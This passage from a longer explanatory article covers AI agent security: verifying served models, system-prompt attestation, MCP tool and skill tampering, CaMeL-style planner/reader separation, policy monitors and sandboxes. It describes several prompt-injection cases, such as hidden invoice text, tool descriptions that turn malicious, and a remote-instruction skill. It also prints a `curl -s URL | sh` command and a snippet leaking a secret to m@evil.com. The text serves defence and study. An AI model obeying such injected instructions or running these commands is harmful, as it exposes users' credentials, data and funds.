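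Karvonen and colleagues instead measure whether the differences are small enough to be rounding. Their method, Token-DiFR, requires the provider and the checker to use the same random seed. The model gives each possible next token $i$ a score $\ell_i$. The server adds random noise $g_i$, scaled by a setting called temperature $T$, and picks the token with the highest total:

$$z_i = \ell_i + T g_i.$$

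The checker feeds the whole answer through a trusted copy of the model, which is faster than generating it, and calculates the same totals. For each token $t$ that the provider reported, the discrepancy is

$$\delta = \max_i z_i - z_t.$$

Suppose the checker's best choice is "unpaid", with a score of 21.40, but the provider wrote "overdue". If "overdue" scores 21.39, the discrepancy of 0.01 could easily be rounding, but if it scores 17.00, the discrepancy of 4.40 is hard to explain that way. More than 98% of tokens match exactly, so the checker averages the discrepancy over many tokens and compares the result with a threshold taken from honest runs.

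The researchers tested whether this could expose a provider that secretly used a cheaper copy of the model, with weights compressed to four bits. With 300 tokens, the method achieved an AUC above 0.999, which means that a batch of text from the compressed copy would have a larger discrepancy than a batch from the original model more than 99.9% of the time.

Detection is harder when the provider and the checker use different graphics chips. The researchers allowed false alarms on at most 1% of honest batches. For Llama 3.1 8B, the method still reliably caught all four changes they tried, but it needed up to a few thousand tokens. For Qwen3-30B-A3B, it caught the large changes but had trouble distinguishing a slightly higher temperature from ordinary variation between chips.

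Cryptographic proofs of the whole calculation would not need a threshold, but one system that Karvonen and colleagues cite took about 2,646 seconds per token for a fairly small model.

Re-running works best for open models. Dittmar and colleagues had no copy of Apple's weights, so they could only repeat some of their questions between December 2025 and March 2026 and see that the answers stayed the same. Apple could give an auditor the weights, but the auditor would also need the employee's email and the summary, which PCC is designed to keep from everyone except the user.

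## Checking an agent's model, tools and prompt before each request

A server's behavior can change when someone rewrites the system prompt, even if the server still runs exactly the software and weights its operator promised. This happened to xAI's chatbot, Grok, in May 2025.

### The change to Grok's prompt

Grok replies to users' posts on the social network X. At about 3:15 a.m. Pacific time on 14 May, someone changed its system prompt to make it give a particular response on a political topic, according to an xAI statement quoted by VentureBeat. For a few hours, Grok brought up "white genocide" in South Africa in answers to unrelated questions. xAI called the change unauthorised. It already had a review process for prompt changes, but whoever made this one bypassed it, according to Engadget's *Grok kept talking about 'white genocide' due to an 'unauthorized modification'*. xAI didn't explain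 how that person had such extensive access or why nobody noticed at first (heise online's *Manipulation of the system prompt*).

xAI promised extra checks and a round-the-clock monitoring team. It also began publishing Grok's prompts on GitHub so that the public could comment on every change. Publication makes a bad change easier to spot but doesn't prevent one, and The Decoder (2025) reports that xAI later reversed other prompt changes after Grok gave racist responses. Nor does a file on GitHub prove that the running service uses that file.

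A hash can close part of this gap. The company records the hash of the prompt it has approved, $h_{\text{approved}}$. Before each request, a program outside the model hashes the prompt $s$ that is about to be used and calls the model only if

$$H(s) = h_{\text{approved}}.$$

This check works only if the person who can edit the prompt can't also edit the recorded hash. It also doesn't help if the company approves a bad prompt.

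### Five layers around an agent

Nguyen and Husain (2026), in *Agent Trust Infrastructure (ATI)*, built this check into a larger system for agents that work across organisations. They simulated eight organisations with five agents each, modelled on university offices: admissions, financial aid, the registrar, advising and a liaison. Only the liaison could contact another organisation. Five layers, which the researchers call planes, handled each request:

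1. **Identity.** The sender must sign the request with a private key. Its identifier is the hash of the matching public key, so it can't choose another agent's identifier.
2. **Trust.** The sender needs a certificate from its own organisation's certificate authority. The layer rejects expired certificates, authorities that vouch for someone else's organisation, and partners whose access has been withdrawn.
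3. **Attestation.** The agent about to answer must have its approved model, tools and system prompt.
4. **Policy.** This layer checks every database read and write. For example, an organisation may read another's records but not change them.
5. **Accountability.** This layer blocks nothing. It adds each allowed read or write to a signed log, in which every entry includes the hash of the one before.

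All five are ordinary code outside the model. Together they took about 174 microseconds for a request with one tool call, while a model usually takes seconds to reply.

The attestation layer makes three comparisons against values recorded when the agent was set up. If one fails, the model never receives the request.

| Component | What the layer compares | How the researchers attacked it |
|---|---|---|
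| Model | The running model with the approved one | They swapped in GPT-3.5-Turbo |
| Web search tool | The names of its module and function | They substituted a tool that returned false content and an instruction to leak data |
| System prompt | Its SHA-256 hash | They added a hidden instruction |

### What the layers stopped

Nguyen and Husain tried 14 attacks, using two of the eight organisations. They ran each attack three times with each of five wordings on each of five models, for 75 trials per attack. They left out a few trials that failed for technical reasons. Five judge models then voted on whether the attack had been stopped. The judges agreed on 96% of their votes, but four of them were also among the models tested, so a model could judge its own trials.

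The researchers added the layers one at a time. These are some of the results, as the percentage of trials in which the attack failed:

| Attack | No defence | Identity and trust | Attestation added | Policy added |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Stolen or forged certificate | 53 | 100 | 100 | 100 |
| Replaced model | 0 | 0 | 100 | 100 |
| Replaced tool | 79 | 81 | 100 | 100 |
| Altered system prompt | 27 | 27 | 100 | 100 |
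| Telling another organisation to change its records | 15 | 13 | 16 | 71 |
| Prompt injection | 51 | 52 | 52 | 52 |
| Average of all 14 attacks | 43 | 61 | 76 | 84 |

For three attacks, including the altered system prompt, the researchers measured only the first column and the step that stopped the attack. They inferred the other values from how the checks work. For the 11 attacks they measured at every step, the average rose from 40% to 80%.

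The attestation layer's perfect scores were almost guaranteed by design, since each attack changed something that the code compares. The starting values are more informative. A replaced model always went unnoticed because the substitute did the registrar's work and no model had anything harmful to refuse. An altered prompt sometimes failed even without any defence because the model refused to follow it. Such refusals vary a lot, and results for attacks that no layer targeted changed by 10 to 25 percentage points between steps for no apparent reason. The tool check's gain of 19 points falls within that range, although a simple comparison should stop every tool swap.

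In the prompt injection test, notes in the advising office's data contained a hidden instruction to output a string chosen by the attacker. The defence's average success rate stayed between 51% and 53% throughout, but results varied widely by model. Two models never resisted the attack, and another resisted it 93% of the time. The five models, which included GPT-4o-mini and Claude 3 Haiku, were old or small by late 2026, so these rates are weak evidence about current agents. But the attestation layer wouldn't help a newer model resist the attack either, because it doesn't check the notes.

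The 84% is a plain average, so it depends on which attacks the researchers chose, and most of those concerned identity and permissions. An attacker who knew about the layers would choose prompt injection. But the layers didn't interfere with normal work, since the agents completed 91% of harmless tasks without them and 92% with them.

### What a real deployment would need

Nguyen and Husain acknowledge the simulation's simplifications. The comparisons ran in the same process as the agent, so an attacker who controlled the computer could have falsified them. The tool check compared only names, so altered code with the same names would presumably pass. Comparing hashes of the tools' code would be a stronger check.

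The attestation check also ran only once, when a request first entered the federation. Suppose someone has altered the prompt of the registrar's agent. The liaison passes the check and forwards a request to the registrar's agent, which nobody checks. In a real system, every agent that handles the request would need its own check, and each organisation would have to verify the sender's signature and certificate again.

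The researchers have also released a software package that comes closer to this. The calling organisation puts the approved model, tools and prompt hash into its agent's identity token. The computer running the agent then sends a signed report of the current values with each request, and the receiving organisation checks them against the token. None of the results above come from this package, and a compromised computer could still sign a false report. Hardware-backed measurement, as in Apple's servers, would make the report harder to fake. *Trusted Model Environment for Private Semantic Computations* (2026) describes a design in which protected hardware signs a record that ties the output to the model, the inputs and a fixed system prompt.

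An organisation that rents a model from a provider can't hash the weights, so it may check the "running model" only by reading the name the provider reports. Signed replies don't solve this. *AEX* (2026) proposes a way to sign the replies of hosted models, but states that it doesn't prove which weights produced a reply or that the provider added no hidden prompt.

A truthful report shows the receiver that the caller's agent is running the prompt the caller approved, but not whether its instructions are sensible, because the receiver sees only a hash of the prompt. *Risks and controls for multi-agent systems* (Reid, O'Callaghan and colleagues, 2026), written for the Australian government, points out that interactions between agents from different organisations can lead to failures that no single organisation's controls can reach. It lists standards for agent identity among the things still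 missing.

### Tools that change after approval

The tool in the experiment ran inside the simulation, but many agents use tools that strangers maintain. Agents usually connect to these tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard that Anthropic introduced in 2024. An MCP server sends the agent's harness each tool's name, a description and a schema listing the inputs it accepts. The harness passes these to the model, so a tool's description can also contain instructions to the model.

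In September 2025, Koi Security reported on an MCP server for the email service Postmark. An independent developer had published it, and for fifteen versions it did only what he claimed. Version 1.0.16 began copying every email to his own server, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Malicious AI Agent Server Reportedly Steals Emails*. Pinning an earlier release, which means staying on that approved version until someone approves another, would have protected users.

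A server can also change what it sends without releasing a new version. *Deadbugz* (Fogel, 2026) describes a server that offered two harmless tools, for formatting and summarising text. After an agent had made three tool calls, the server replaced the tools' descriptions with instructions to look for passwords and keys on the user's computer and hide this from the user. The instructions had been in the server's code all along, so a hash of that code would have stayed the same, and a short test would have found nothing wrong. The attacker opened 23 pull requests on GitHub to add the server to other people's projects, and none had been merged when Fogel's team reviewed them.

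Many of these servers run on someone else's computer, so the user can pin only an address. Red Hat (2026) warns that the server's owner can then change what it returns without any change to the user's files that would trigger a review. Fogel recommends storing a fingerprint of the tool definitions when the user approves them, comparing it with what the server sends later, and asking the user again if they differ. This check would have caught the switch after the third call.

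Changes to MCP servers are common, and most are innocent. In *Same Name, Different Server*, Kraishan (2026) examined all 21,643 servers in the public MCP registry in August 2026. Of the 8,900 with more than one version, 40.6% had made a "silent" change, most often a rewritten server description. That figure includes the 4.2% that had moved to a different host under the same name. Kraishan thinks most of the moves were routine, and he found no obvious hidden instructions in tool descriptions when he scanned the code of 14,353 servers. But the registry doesn't record tool definitions, so nobody can use it to see when they changed.

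*SchemaCaps* (Ameur, Bouzefrane and Banerjee, 2026) surveyed eight products that use or scan MCP tools to see whether they ask for approval again when an approved tool begins to accept new inputs. Six didn't, and the researchers couldn't determine what the other two did. Microsoft's code editor VS Code, for example, ties approval to the tool's name. The researchers also found a real update to a command-line tool that added an input for choosing which shell would run the agent's commands. A company's rules for commands in one shell might not work in another.

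Asking about every change has a cost. The researchers replayed 604 releases of 39 servers, published over 21 months, under several rules:

| When the user has to approve an existing tool again | Approvals |
|---|---|
| After any change to its definition | 2,004 |
| After any change to its schema | 1,197 |
| After a schema change that might let the agent do more | 645 |

The first rule produces about 51 questions per server, and people who see that many may stop reading them. The last rule, which is the researchers' own, cuts that number by two-thirds, partly by ignoring descriptions. But new descriptions alone were enough to make the Deadbugz server malicious.

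None of these rules detects a tool whose behavior changes while its definition stays the same. *ProbeID* (2026) reports repeated tests of tools on 16 servers, in which seven tools began to give different answers while every server kept the same version number. Different answers don't necessarily mean an attack, since one of these tools reported current conditions, which are supposed to change.

### Pinning and signing skills

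A skill is a folder of instructions, often with scripts, that an agent follows to do a particular job. Skills are easier to pin than remote tools because the user has the files. *Agent Skill Evolution* (2026), a study of 3,159 skills, found that most revisions were substantive, changing a rule or a procedure. In August 2026, TechRadar's *Experts warn malicious AI skills are hitting more victims than ever* described attackers who copied existing skills and then used updates to add code that steals credentials.

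GitHub (2026) introduced a command in April that can pin a skill to an exact version. The command also records a hash of the skill's folder to detect changes to its contents, even if the version number stays the same. Publishers can also make a release permanent, so that someone who takes over their account can't alter it. GitHub doesn't verify the skills and warns that they may contain malicious scripts or hidden instructions.

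NVIDIA signs its skills with the same OpenSSF format it uses for models. The signature covers the skill's whole folder, and a strict check fails if anyone adds a file. NVIDIA's *Verify Signed Agent Skills* says that signing "does not prove a skill is safe", and advises publishers to scan and review a skill before signing it.

In June 2026, the security company AIR showed that a skill's files may reveal little about what the skill will make an agent do. AIR published a harmless skill that sent agents to an outside web page for further instructions. Every scanner AIR tried, including those from Cisco and NVIDIA, marked the skill as safe. AIR then changed the page. The company says the skill reached about 26,000 agents and collected only users' email addresses (Constantin, 2026, *A fake AI agent skill passed every security scanner*). A pinned hash or a signature would have stayed valid because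 the skill's files never changed. A reviewer could reject any skill that takes instructions from an outside page, but that would also exclude the many legitimate skills that send agents to online documentation.

Pinning also helps with investigations, provided the agent's records include the version. *Harnessing Agent Skills* (2026) found that the event records of two popular coding agents, Claude Code and Codex, include the name of the skill an agent used but not its revision. After an incident, an investigator might know which skill the agent used without knowing what instructions it contained at the time.

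### Standing instructions and new text

System prompts, skills and tool definitions exist before the task begins. Someone can read them, approve them and record their hashes, and a program can refuse to start the agent if any of them has changed. An email or web page that arrives during the task can't be checked this way, because no one has approved it and recorded its hash beforehand.

A system prompt often includes today's date or the user's name, so its hash would change every day or for every user. The harness can hash the fixed part and fill in the rest afterwards, as long as it controls what it inserts. An agent may also edit its own skills as it learns, which turns text from one task into standing instructions for the next. *Skills as Verifiable Artifacts* (2026) proposes that a loaded skill stay fixed for the whole session. A person would have to approve any edit by the agent, and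 the new version would need verification before the next session.

New text can still be hashed when it arrives. *A2AS* (2025), a proposed security framework for agents, attaches a hash to each incoming prompt, based on its content and origin. The harness can then reject text that was altered in transit, and investigators can trace where an instruction came from. The email with the white text, sent to the agent on the accounts mailbox, would pass this check, because a valid hash shows only that the message hasn't changed since the attacker wrote it.

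## Rules enforced outside the model: the CaMeL system

Nobody can approve an email before it arrives, but a malicious email usually does no harm until the agent acts on it. A company can therefore let the agent read its mail and check what the agent tries to do next. A checkpoint that every relevant action must pass is called a reference monitor, an idea that dates from 1972 according to the slides *Science of Security Historical Perspective*. The monitor has to take control at every event the policy covers, block any event that would violate the policy, and resist tampering. Java's security manager was vulnerable to tampering because a hostile applet could rewrite the manager's private variables.

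The harness is the natural place for an agent's monitor, because the model can act only through tool calls. The monitor also needs a policy, a written rule outside the model about which actions the agent may take. *From Intent to Execution Grant* (2026) points out that the concept of a reference monitor doesn't specify what that policy should contain.

### Forbidden steps and required steps

*Enforceable Security Policies* (Schneider, 2000) analyzes what a monitor can achieve by watching a program's steps and stopping the program when the next step would break the policy. Its decisions can depend only on what has happened so far, not on what the program will do later or would have done with different input.

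This monitor can enforce only safety properties, which are rules that a program always breaks at some definite step, with no way to make up for it afterwards. Let $\sigma$ be a run that breaks the rule, $\sigma[..i]$ its first $i$ steps, and $\tau$ any continuation. Then

$$\sigma \text{ breaks the rule} \;\Rightarrow\; \exists i\;\forall \tau:\; \sigma[..i]\,\tau \text{ breaks the rule}.$$

Schneider's example forbids a program from sending messages after it has read a file. The monitor only has to record whether the program has read a file and, if it has, block any message it tries to send. *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (2026) applies the same idea to agents, with rules that can depend on which model call produced a message and which approvals came before an action.

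A monitor can't enforce a rule that every customer with an unpaid invoice must eventually get a reminder just by stopping the agent. However long the agent has waited, it might still send the reminder next, so the monitor never reaches a step at which the rule is definitely broken. A deadline would let the monitor detect the failure, but stopping the agent at that point still wouldn't send the reminder. By contrast, a monitor that refused every tool call would enforce any prohibition perfectly, so a security result means little unless it is reported with the share of tasks the agent completed.

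Protecting secrets is also difficult. A single run can't show whether an email reveals a bank balance, because that depends on whether the agent would have written something else if the balance had been different. The monitor can instead enforce a stricter rule, such as blocking every email that contains anything derived from the balance, but this also blocks some harmless emails.

### One invoice and two models

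CaMeL, which Debenedetti and colleagues at Google DeepMind presented in 2025, enforces stricter rules of this kind. It builds on a 2023 proposal by the programmer Simon Willison to divide an agent between two models, one that has the tools and one without tools that reads all untrusted text. Willison (2025) explains in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks* how CaMeL repaired a flaw in his design.

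Suppose an employee writes, "Pay Harbour Print's March invoice. It's attached to their last email." An attacker has broken into the supplier's mailbox and sent an altered invoice. It gives the attacker's account number, and a line of hidden text tells the agent to forward all the company's other invoices to an outside address. CaMeL would handle the request like this:

1. The planning model receives the employee's request and a description of the tools, but not the email. It writes a short program in a restricted version of Python:

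```
email   = get_last_email(sender="Harbour Print")
invoice = ask_reader("Find the amount and account", email)
send_money(to=invoice.account, amount=invoice.amount)
```

2. CaMeL's interpreter runs the first line and marks `email` as untrusted, because it came from outside.
3. The reading model extracts the amount and the account number. It has no tools, so the hidden text can't make it forward anything. At worst, it returns false values. The interpreter marks `invoice` as untrusted too, because it came from `email`.
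4. Before the payment, the interpreter applies the policy for `send_money`. If the policy requires an account number from the employee or from the company's own supplier list, the interpreter refuses the payment or asks the employee to approve it.

The instruction to forward the invoices fails because the program contains no such step, and the instruction never reached the model that wrote the program. The false account number is harder to stop because the employee did ask for a payment, so the attacker only has to change the data. Willison's original design would have let the false number through. CaMeL catches it with the marks, called capabilities, which record where each value came from and who may read it.

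The same policy would block payment of a legitimate invoice. A better plan would look up the account in the supplier list and take only the amount from the attachment, but then the attacker could inflate the amount. One rule in *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026) rejects a payment if either the recipient or the amount comes from an untrusted source. Under that rule, the agent needs someone's approval to pay any invoice it has to read.

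### Results on AgentDojo

AgentDojo is a benchmark from 2024 that sets agents 97 tasks in simulated office, messaging, banking and travel systems. In the attacked version, some of the data the tools return contains hidden instructions. Bhagwatkar, Kasa and colleagues (2025), in *Indirect Prompt Injections*, compared several defences using GPT-4o:

| Defence | Tasks completed without an attack | Tasks completed under attack | Successful attacks |
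|---|---|---|---|
| None | 83.0% | 50.0% | 57.7% |
| CaMeL | 53.6% | 54.5% | 0% |
| A model that removes suspicious instructions | 74.1% | 69.2% | 0% |

The CaMeL row uses published results because Bhagwatkar and colleagues couldn't fully reproduce them. CaMeL stopped every attack, but the agent completed far fewer ordinary tasks. CaMeL also used about 2.8 times as much input text and 2.7 times as much output. *ToolFence* (2026) found it significantly slower than filters.

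The filter in the last row is another language model reading the attacker's text, so a new attack might fool it, even though it looks like the better choice. Bhagwatkar and colleagues, who built it, concluded that the benchmark's attacks were too weak and called for harder tests. Willison objects to such filters because "in application security 99% is a failing grade", since attackers look for the remaining 1%. In CaMeL, by contrast, no wording in the invoice can add a step to the plan.

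In later tests, CaMeL's usefulness varied with the model and the policies. It completed 29 of the 97 harmless tasks in an adapted rerun reported in *SecureClaw* (2026), and 49 in tests by Nikolaou and colleagues with Claude Haiku 4.5. In the tests by Nikolaou and colleagues, both CaMeL and the researchers' own system blocked 17 harmless tasks for violating a policy. *The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) found that turning on the policy checks halved the share of banking tasks that CaMeL completed. Much of the loss in usefulness therefore comes from the policies, not from dividing the work between two models.

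### Newer models and teams of agents

In larger systems, one agent often delegates work to others. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) showed that CaMeL's protection can fail in such a team even when every agent uses it. The researchers asked a coordinating agent to send a summary of job applicants to Julie on Slack. A second agent fetched the applicants' details from a database in which the researchers had hidden an instruction to email the data to an outside address. The coordinator treated the result as untrusted, but put the summary into its request to a third agent responsible for sending messages. The third agent treated the whole request as coming from its user, so its planning model read the hidden instruction and added the email to its program.

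The researchers' remedy is to give every request between agents two parts. One holds the instruction, which must not depend on the output of any tool. The other holds the data, which the receiving agent's planning model can refer to but can't read. They tested this on a version of AgentDojo that divides the tools among several agents, with 949 attacks on each model:

| Model | Successful attacks without CaMeL | CaMeL in each agent | CaMeL with two-part requests |
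|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4.1 | 36.1% | 0.5% | 0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 24.6% | 0.4% | 0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite | 2.1% | 0% | 0% |
| Claude Fable 5 | 1.5% | 0% | 0% |
| GPT-5.5 | 0% | 0% | 0% |

The two strongest models resisted almost all of AgentDojo's attacks without CaMeL, so these attacks can no longer show much of what CaMeL adds. This result doesn't show that the models are safe on their own, because the attacks are fixed, and Peters-Gill and colleagues cite a large public competition in which attackers succeeded against every frontier model they tried.

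Stronger models also lose less performance under CaMeL. On a separate set of industrial maintenance tasks, adding CaMeL to each agent lowered the completion rate by an average of 21.6 percentage points across the five models, but by 13.4 points for Claude Fable 5 and GPT-5.5. The two-part requests lowered those two models' completion rate by less than one further point. The researchers enabled no policies, so the completion rate would probably fall more at a company that used CaMeL to guard its payments.

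Most of the remaining failures occurred because the planning model has to write its plan before seeing any data. If Harbour Print's email says that the invoice is in a shared folder, an ordinary agent can open the folder, but CaMeL can do so only if the plan already covers that possibility.

### Leaks through the plan's branches

CaMeL would refuse to send an email on the condition that a secret balance is above some threshold, since the email would reveal the answer. Garby and colleagues found that a program can get the same information out indirectly:

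```
tmp = True
rich = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

When the balance is high, `tmp` becomes false and the program skips the line that would change `rich`. CaMeL marks a variable only when the program changes it, so `rich` never gets the "secret" mark, and the email goes out. When the balance is low, `rich` becomes false and the program sends no email. An attacker can't normally write the plan, so the leak depends on the planning model producing code like this, but it shows that the interpreter's tracking is incomplete.

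Garby and colleagues designed a small programming language for agents that tracks such flows and proved its guarantee in Lean. Their agent resisted all but two of 1,296 attacks on AgentDojo's banking tasks and completed about as many tasks as CaMeL did with its policies turned off.

An attacker may also be able to choose among the steps a plan already contains. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) extends CaMeL to agents that operate a computer through its screen. A plan for such an agent has to allow for interruptions like cookie notices, so the researchers disguised an advertisement as a cookie notice. The plan stayed the same, but the agent clicked where the attacker wanted. Comparing the screen image with the page's code stopped only some of these advertisements.

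### Checking the plan before it runs

CaMeL's plans also offer a way around part of Schneider's limit, which applies to monitors that observe only the steps taken so far. Schneider explicitly excluded tools that analyse a program in advance. An ordinary agent chooses each step after seeing the result of the last, so it has no program to analyse. CaMeL writes the whole plan before running it, so such a tool could check the plan first.

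The system by Nikolaou and colleagues, also called CaMeLoT, turns the plan into a diagram of all the paths it could take, and a standard verification program checks every path against the rules. Their example is an agent that handles security alerts, with a rule that it must resolve or escalate every ticket it opens:

$$\mathbf{AG}\big(\text{create ticket} \Rightarrow \mathbf{AF}(\text{resolve} \lor \text{escalate})\big).$$

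$\mathbf{AG}$ means "at every point on every path", and $\mathbf{AF}$ means "eventually, on every path". If some path leaves a ticket open, CaMeLoT shows that path to the planning model, which can repair the plan before any tool runs.

CaMeLoT caught all seven unsafe plans the researchers had written, while a simplified version of CaMeL caught one. This gap was expected because the researchers had chosen rules that CaMeL can't easily express. On AgentDojo, CaMeLoT could check 22 of CaMeL's 28 policies in advance. Others depend on facts that can change, such as who can read a shared file when the agent sends it. A planned step can also still fail, since the ticket system might be down when the agent gets there.

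### Signing the policy with the request

An outsider still has to trust the company's account of which policy was in force. In *KNOX*, Duddu, Caulfield and He (2026) designed a system that provides evidence of which policy applied. They built it for the supervised trials of AI systems that the EU's AI Act requires member states to offer, where a regulator may not trust the developer's own report.

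KNOX runs the models and the monitor inside trusted execution environments. A planning model turns the user's request into an ordered list of expected tool calls. KNOX adds the privacy laws that apply, the system functions the tools may use, and the conditions for stopping. The hardware then signs evidence that the resulting policy came from that request.

When the agent proposes an action $\alpha$, the monitor compares it with the next expected call $e_j$ and lets it through only if

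$$H(\alpha) = H(e_j).$$

The tool, its inputs and its place in the sequence must all match. KNOX records every decision in a chain of hashes, and a single hardware signature covers the whole chain. An auditor can confirm that the request, the policy and the actions belong together, and that nobody has removed a refused action from the record.

In simulated tasks, this comparison stopped every departure from the plan and allowed every expected call, as an exact comparison should. For privacy law, the monitor has to use a language model to determine whether a disclosure is legal. The monitor blocked every illegal disclosure by two of the agents tested, but only 81.8% of those by the third. The checks and signatures added less than 1% to the running time, not counting the overhead of the protected hardware itself. The monitor can't detect what a tool does once it has started, so KNOX relies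 on the operating system to limit that.

Exact matching is a severe restriction. The amount on Harbour Print's invoice isn't available to the planner until someone opens the invoice, so the planner can't list the payment correctly in advance. Duddu and colleagues accept that KNOX will block some legitimate actions, because in a trial the share of blocked actions is useful evidence for the regulator. A company that needs its invoices paid would tolerate fewer blocked actions. Also, if the planner misinterprets the request, the hardware will still sign the wrong policy.

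### Evidence from independent services

Some actions look correct, but whether they are depends on a fact that neither the agent nor the monitor can observe. For example, a command to release software can have the right form even though the software failed its tests. *Governing Actions, Not Agents* (Salfeld-Nebgen, 2026) proposes requiring an agent to collect signed evidence before taking such an action.

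The agent first tells a central service, the hub, that it wants to release the software, and the hub gives this request a random identifier. The agent then goes to three independent services:

| Service | What the example policy requires |
|---|---|
| Automated testing | All tests passed, and they covered at least 80% of the code |
| Code review | At least two approvals and no unresolved comments |
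| Security scanning | No critical or high-severity vulnerabilities |

Each service signs its result, the identifier and an expiry time. The hub checks the signatures, applies the policy and either releases the software or gives the agent a narrow permission to release it. The agent can't forge these signatures, and it can't reuse earlier results because the identifier would be wrong. In the published example, the signed results don't include a hash of the software. A real system would have to add one or tie the identifier to a particular version. Otherwise, an agent could have one version tested and release another.

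The same arrangement would help with the altered invoice. The supplier register could sign a statement that the account belongs to Harbour Print, and the purchasing system could sign the amount the company agreed to pay. The attacker would then have to corrupt those systems instead of manipulating a model.

Salfeld-Nebgen has published a working prototype but no measurements, and acknowledges gaps in the model. A service may sign something false, a fact may change before the evidence expires, or an agent could split a harmful goal into steps that each have valid evidence. Collecting several signatures also takes time, so the method suits software releases and prescriptions better than routine actions.

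### Who writes the rules

All these systems need someone to decide what the agent may do. A phone app has a fixed purpose, so its developer can list the permissions it needs, but an agent may get a different request every few minutes. Oswal and Cadeddu (2026) say in *Five Primitives for Governing Autonomous AI Agents at Runtime* that an agent will attempt things nobody anticipated, because that is what people use it for.

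One answer is to write a new policy for each task. *Evolution Under Fire* (2026) describes Progent, which has a model work out from the user's request the narrowest permissions the task needs. For the March invoice, those permissions might cover reading one supplier's email and making one payment. In the SecureClaw comparison, Progent completed 59 of the 97 harmless tasks, twice as many as CaMeL, but at least 20 of the 629 attacks succeeded against it.

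*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) objects that a monitor whose rules come from a language model is only as predictable as the model. This weakness is real but smaller if the model sees only the user's request, because an attacker then can't influence the rules. *ActGov* (2026) limits the damage further by requiring a solver to prove that each policy a model drafts or revises respects a set of fixed rules before the system uses it.

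Another approach is to use an allowlist, which refuses any action the policy doesn't list, and to update the policy based on the refusals. In Oswal and Cadeddu's system, an administrator sees which unlisted actions agents have attempted and can add the useful ones. The system keeps one entry per type of action, because an agent may retry a refused action until it fills the log. It stores the names of the inputs but not their values, because nobody has yet decided which values are confidential. In August 2026, the system was running only in a few private pilots. The first user to need an unlisted action still has to wait for the administrator to add it, and if the monitor fails, every agent that depends on it stops.

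The agent can also ask its user to settle cases that no rule foresaw, but CaMeL's developers acknowledge the danger of asking too often. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) reports that agents that tracked where data came from needed 1.5 to 2.6 times fewer human interventions to complete the same share of tasks. Such tracking could also make the questions better. An employee asked only "Approve payment of €1,200?" may quickly say yes, but would have a reason to telephone the supplier if warned that the account number came from an email attachment and differs from the one on file.

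### What the agent is made of

A permitted action can still come from a compromised agent. Oswal and Cadeddu give the example of an agent in which someone replaced a software component the day before. The agent still identifies itself correctly and requests only actions the policy allows, and the monitor signs a log that is, in their words, "an accurate account of a compromised thing behaving legitimately".

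Authorisation must therefore be combined with checks on the agent's model, tools and prompt. Oswal and Cadeddu's company has a separate product that analyses agents' components, but their monitor doesn't yet check its results before allowing an action. KNOX covers part of this gap, because its evidence contains hashes of the weights of every model involved, including the one that makes judgements about privacy law.

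## Sandboxes and system-call monitoring for agents

A rule about tool calls works well when each call does one thing, such as paying an invoice. But a coding agent mostly uses a single tool that runs whatever command the model has written. The harness handles one call, but the command may run a script that opens a thousand files and starts a dozen other programs. To control those steps, a company has to set limits in the operating system.

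A program can do arithmetic by itself, but it needs the kernel to open a file, connect to another computer or start another program. It requests these services through system calls. The malicious email in the first example made the agent run `curl -s URL | sh`, which on Linux would lead to calls like these:

| System call | What it does here |
|---|---|
| `execve` | Starts `curl` and the shell |
| `connect` | Opens a connection to the attacker's server |
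| `read` and `write` | Pass the download from `curl` to the shell |
| `openat` | Opens any file the downloaded script asks for |

The kernel receives much the same system calls whether an agent runs a command, a person types it, or a Python script does the same job. A limit on system calls therefore applies even to code nobody has seen before.

### Four kinds of sandbox

Cohen and Fogel (2026), in *Your AI Agent Will Run Untrusted Code. Now What?*, reviewed 14 sandboxes for coding agents. They found four kinds, which differ in what separates the agent's code from the host, the computer it runs on:

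| Kind | What separates the code from the host | Example | Main drawback |
|---|---|---|---|
| Process rules | Limits that the host's kernel applies to one process | nono | Suits a user's own computer, not a service with many customers |
| Container | A separate view of files and processes, on the host's own kernel | Daytona, which starts in about 90 milliseconds | A flaw in the kernel can break the boundary |
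| User-space kernel | A program that handles system calls before they reach the host's kernel | gVisor | Security depends on that program being correct |
| MicroVM | A small virtual machine with its own kernel | E2B, which starts in about 150 milliseconds | More memory, and sometimes a limit on session length |

Cohen and Fogel consider microVMs the strongest of the four. An attacker who took over a microVM's kernel would still need a flaw in the program that runs the virtual machine. *Containing the Autonomous Operator* (2026) points out that a single flaw in the shared kernel is enough to escape an ordinary container.

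*Sandlock* (2026) argues that containers and microVMs were designed for long-running services and are excessive for a Python command that finishes in 50 milliseconds. The sandbox it presents uses process rules, needs no administrator rights and is designed to start in under 10 milliseconds.

Andronchik and Lokhmakov (2026), in *AI Code Sandboxes*, measured five products on one server with their default settings. They counted the different system calls that reached the host's kernel while a short data-analysis script ran. They also checked 14 kernel features that attackers have exploited in the past, and ran 28 tests for leaked details of the host, such as its processor model:

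| Product | Kind | Different calls to the host's kernel | Risky features within reach (of 14) | Host details leaked (of 28) |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Arrakis | MicroVM | 8 | 12 | 1 |
| E2B | MicroVM | 13 | 7 | 0 |
| microsandbox | MicroVM | 25 | 11 | 0 |
| gVisor | User-space kernel | 41 | 5 | 2 |
| Daytona | Container | 62 | 11 | 10 |

The calls and leaks vary with the kind of sandbox, but the risky features don't. The risky-features column is easy to misread. A feature reachable in a microVM generally belongs to the virtual machine's own kernel, so an attacker who exploited it would still be inside the virtual machine. Andronchik and Lokhmakov don't combine their measurements into a ranking, because different users face different attackers.

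One study found that updates can matter as much as design. A sandbox product usually builds on an isolation engine that someone else maintains, and a fix to the engine helps only after the product adopts it. In the self-hosted version of E2B, the default engine hadn't changed for 399 days.

In September 2026, TNG Technology Consulting's *AI Insight #5* tested four sandboxes, two of them TNG's own, against six types of attack. None blocked every attack, but each was better than running the agent without a sandbox.

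### Files, network and credentials

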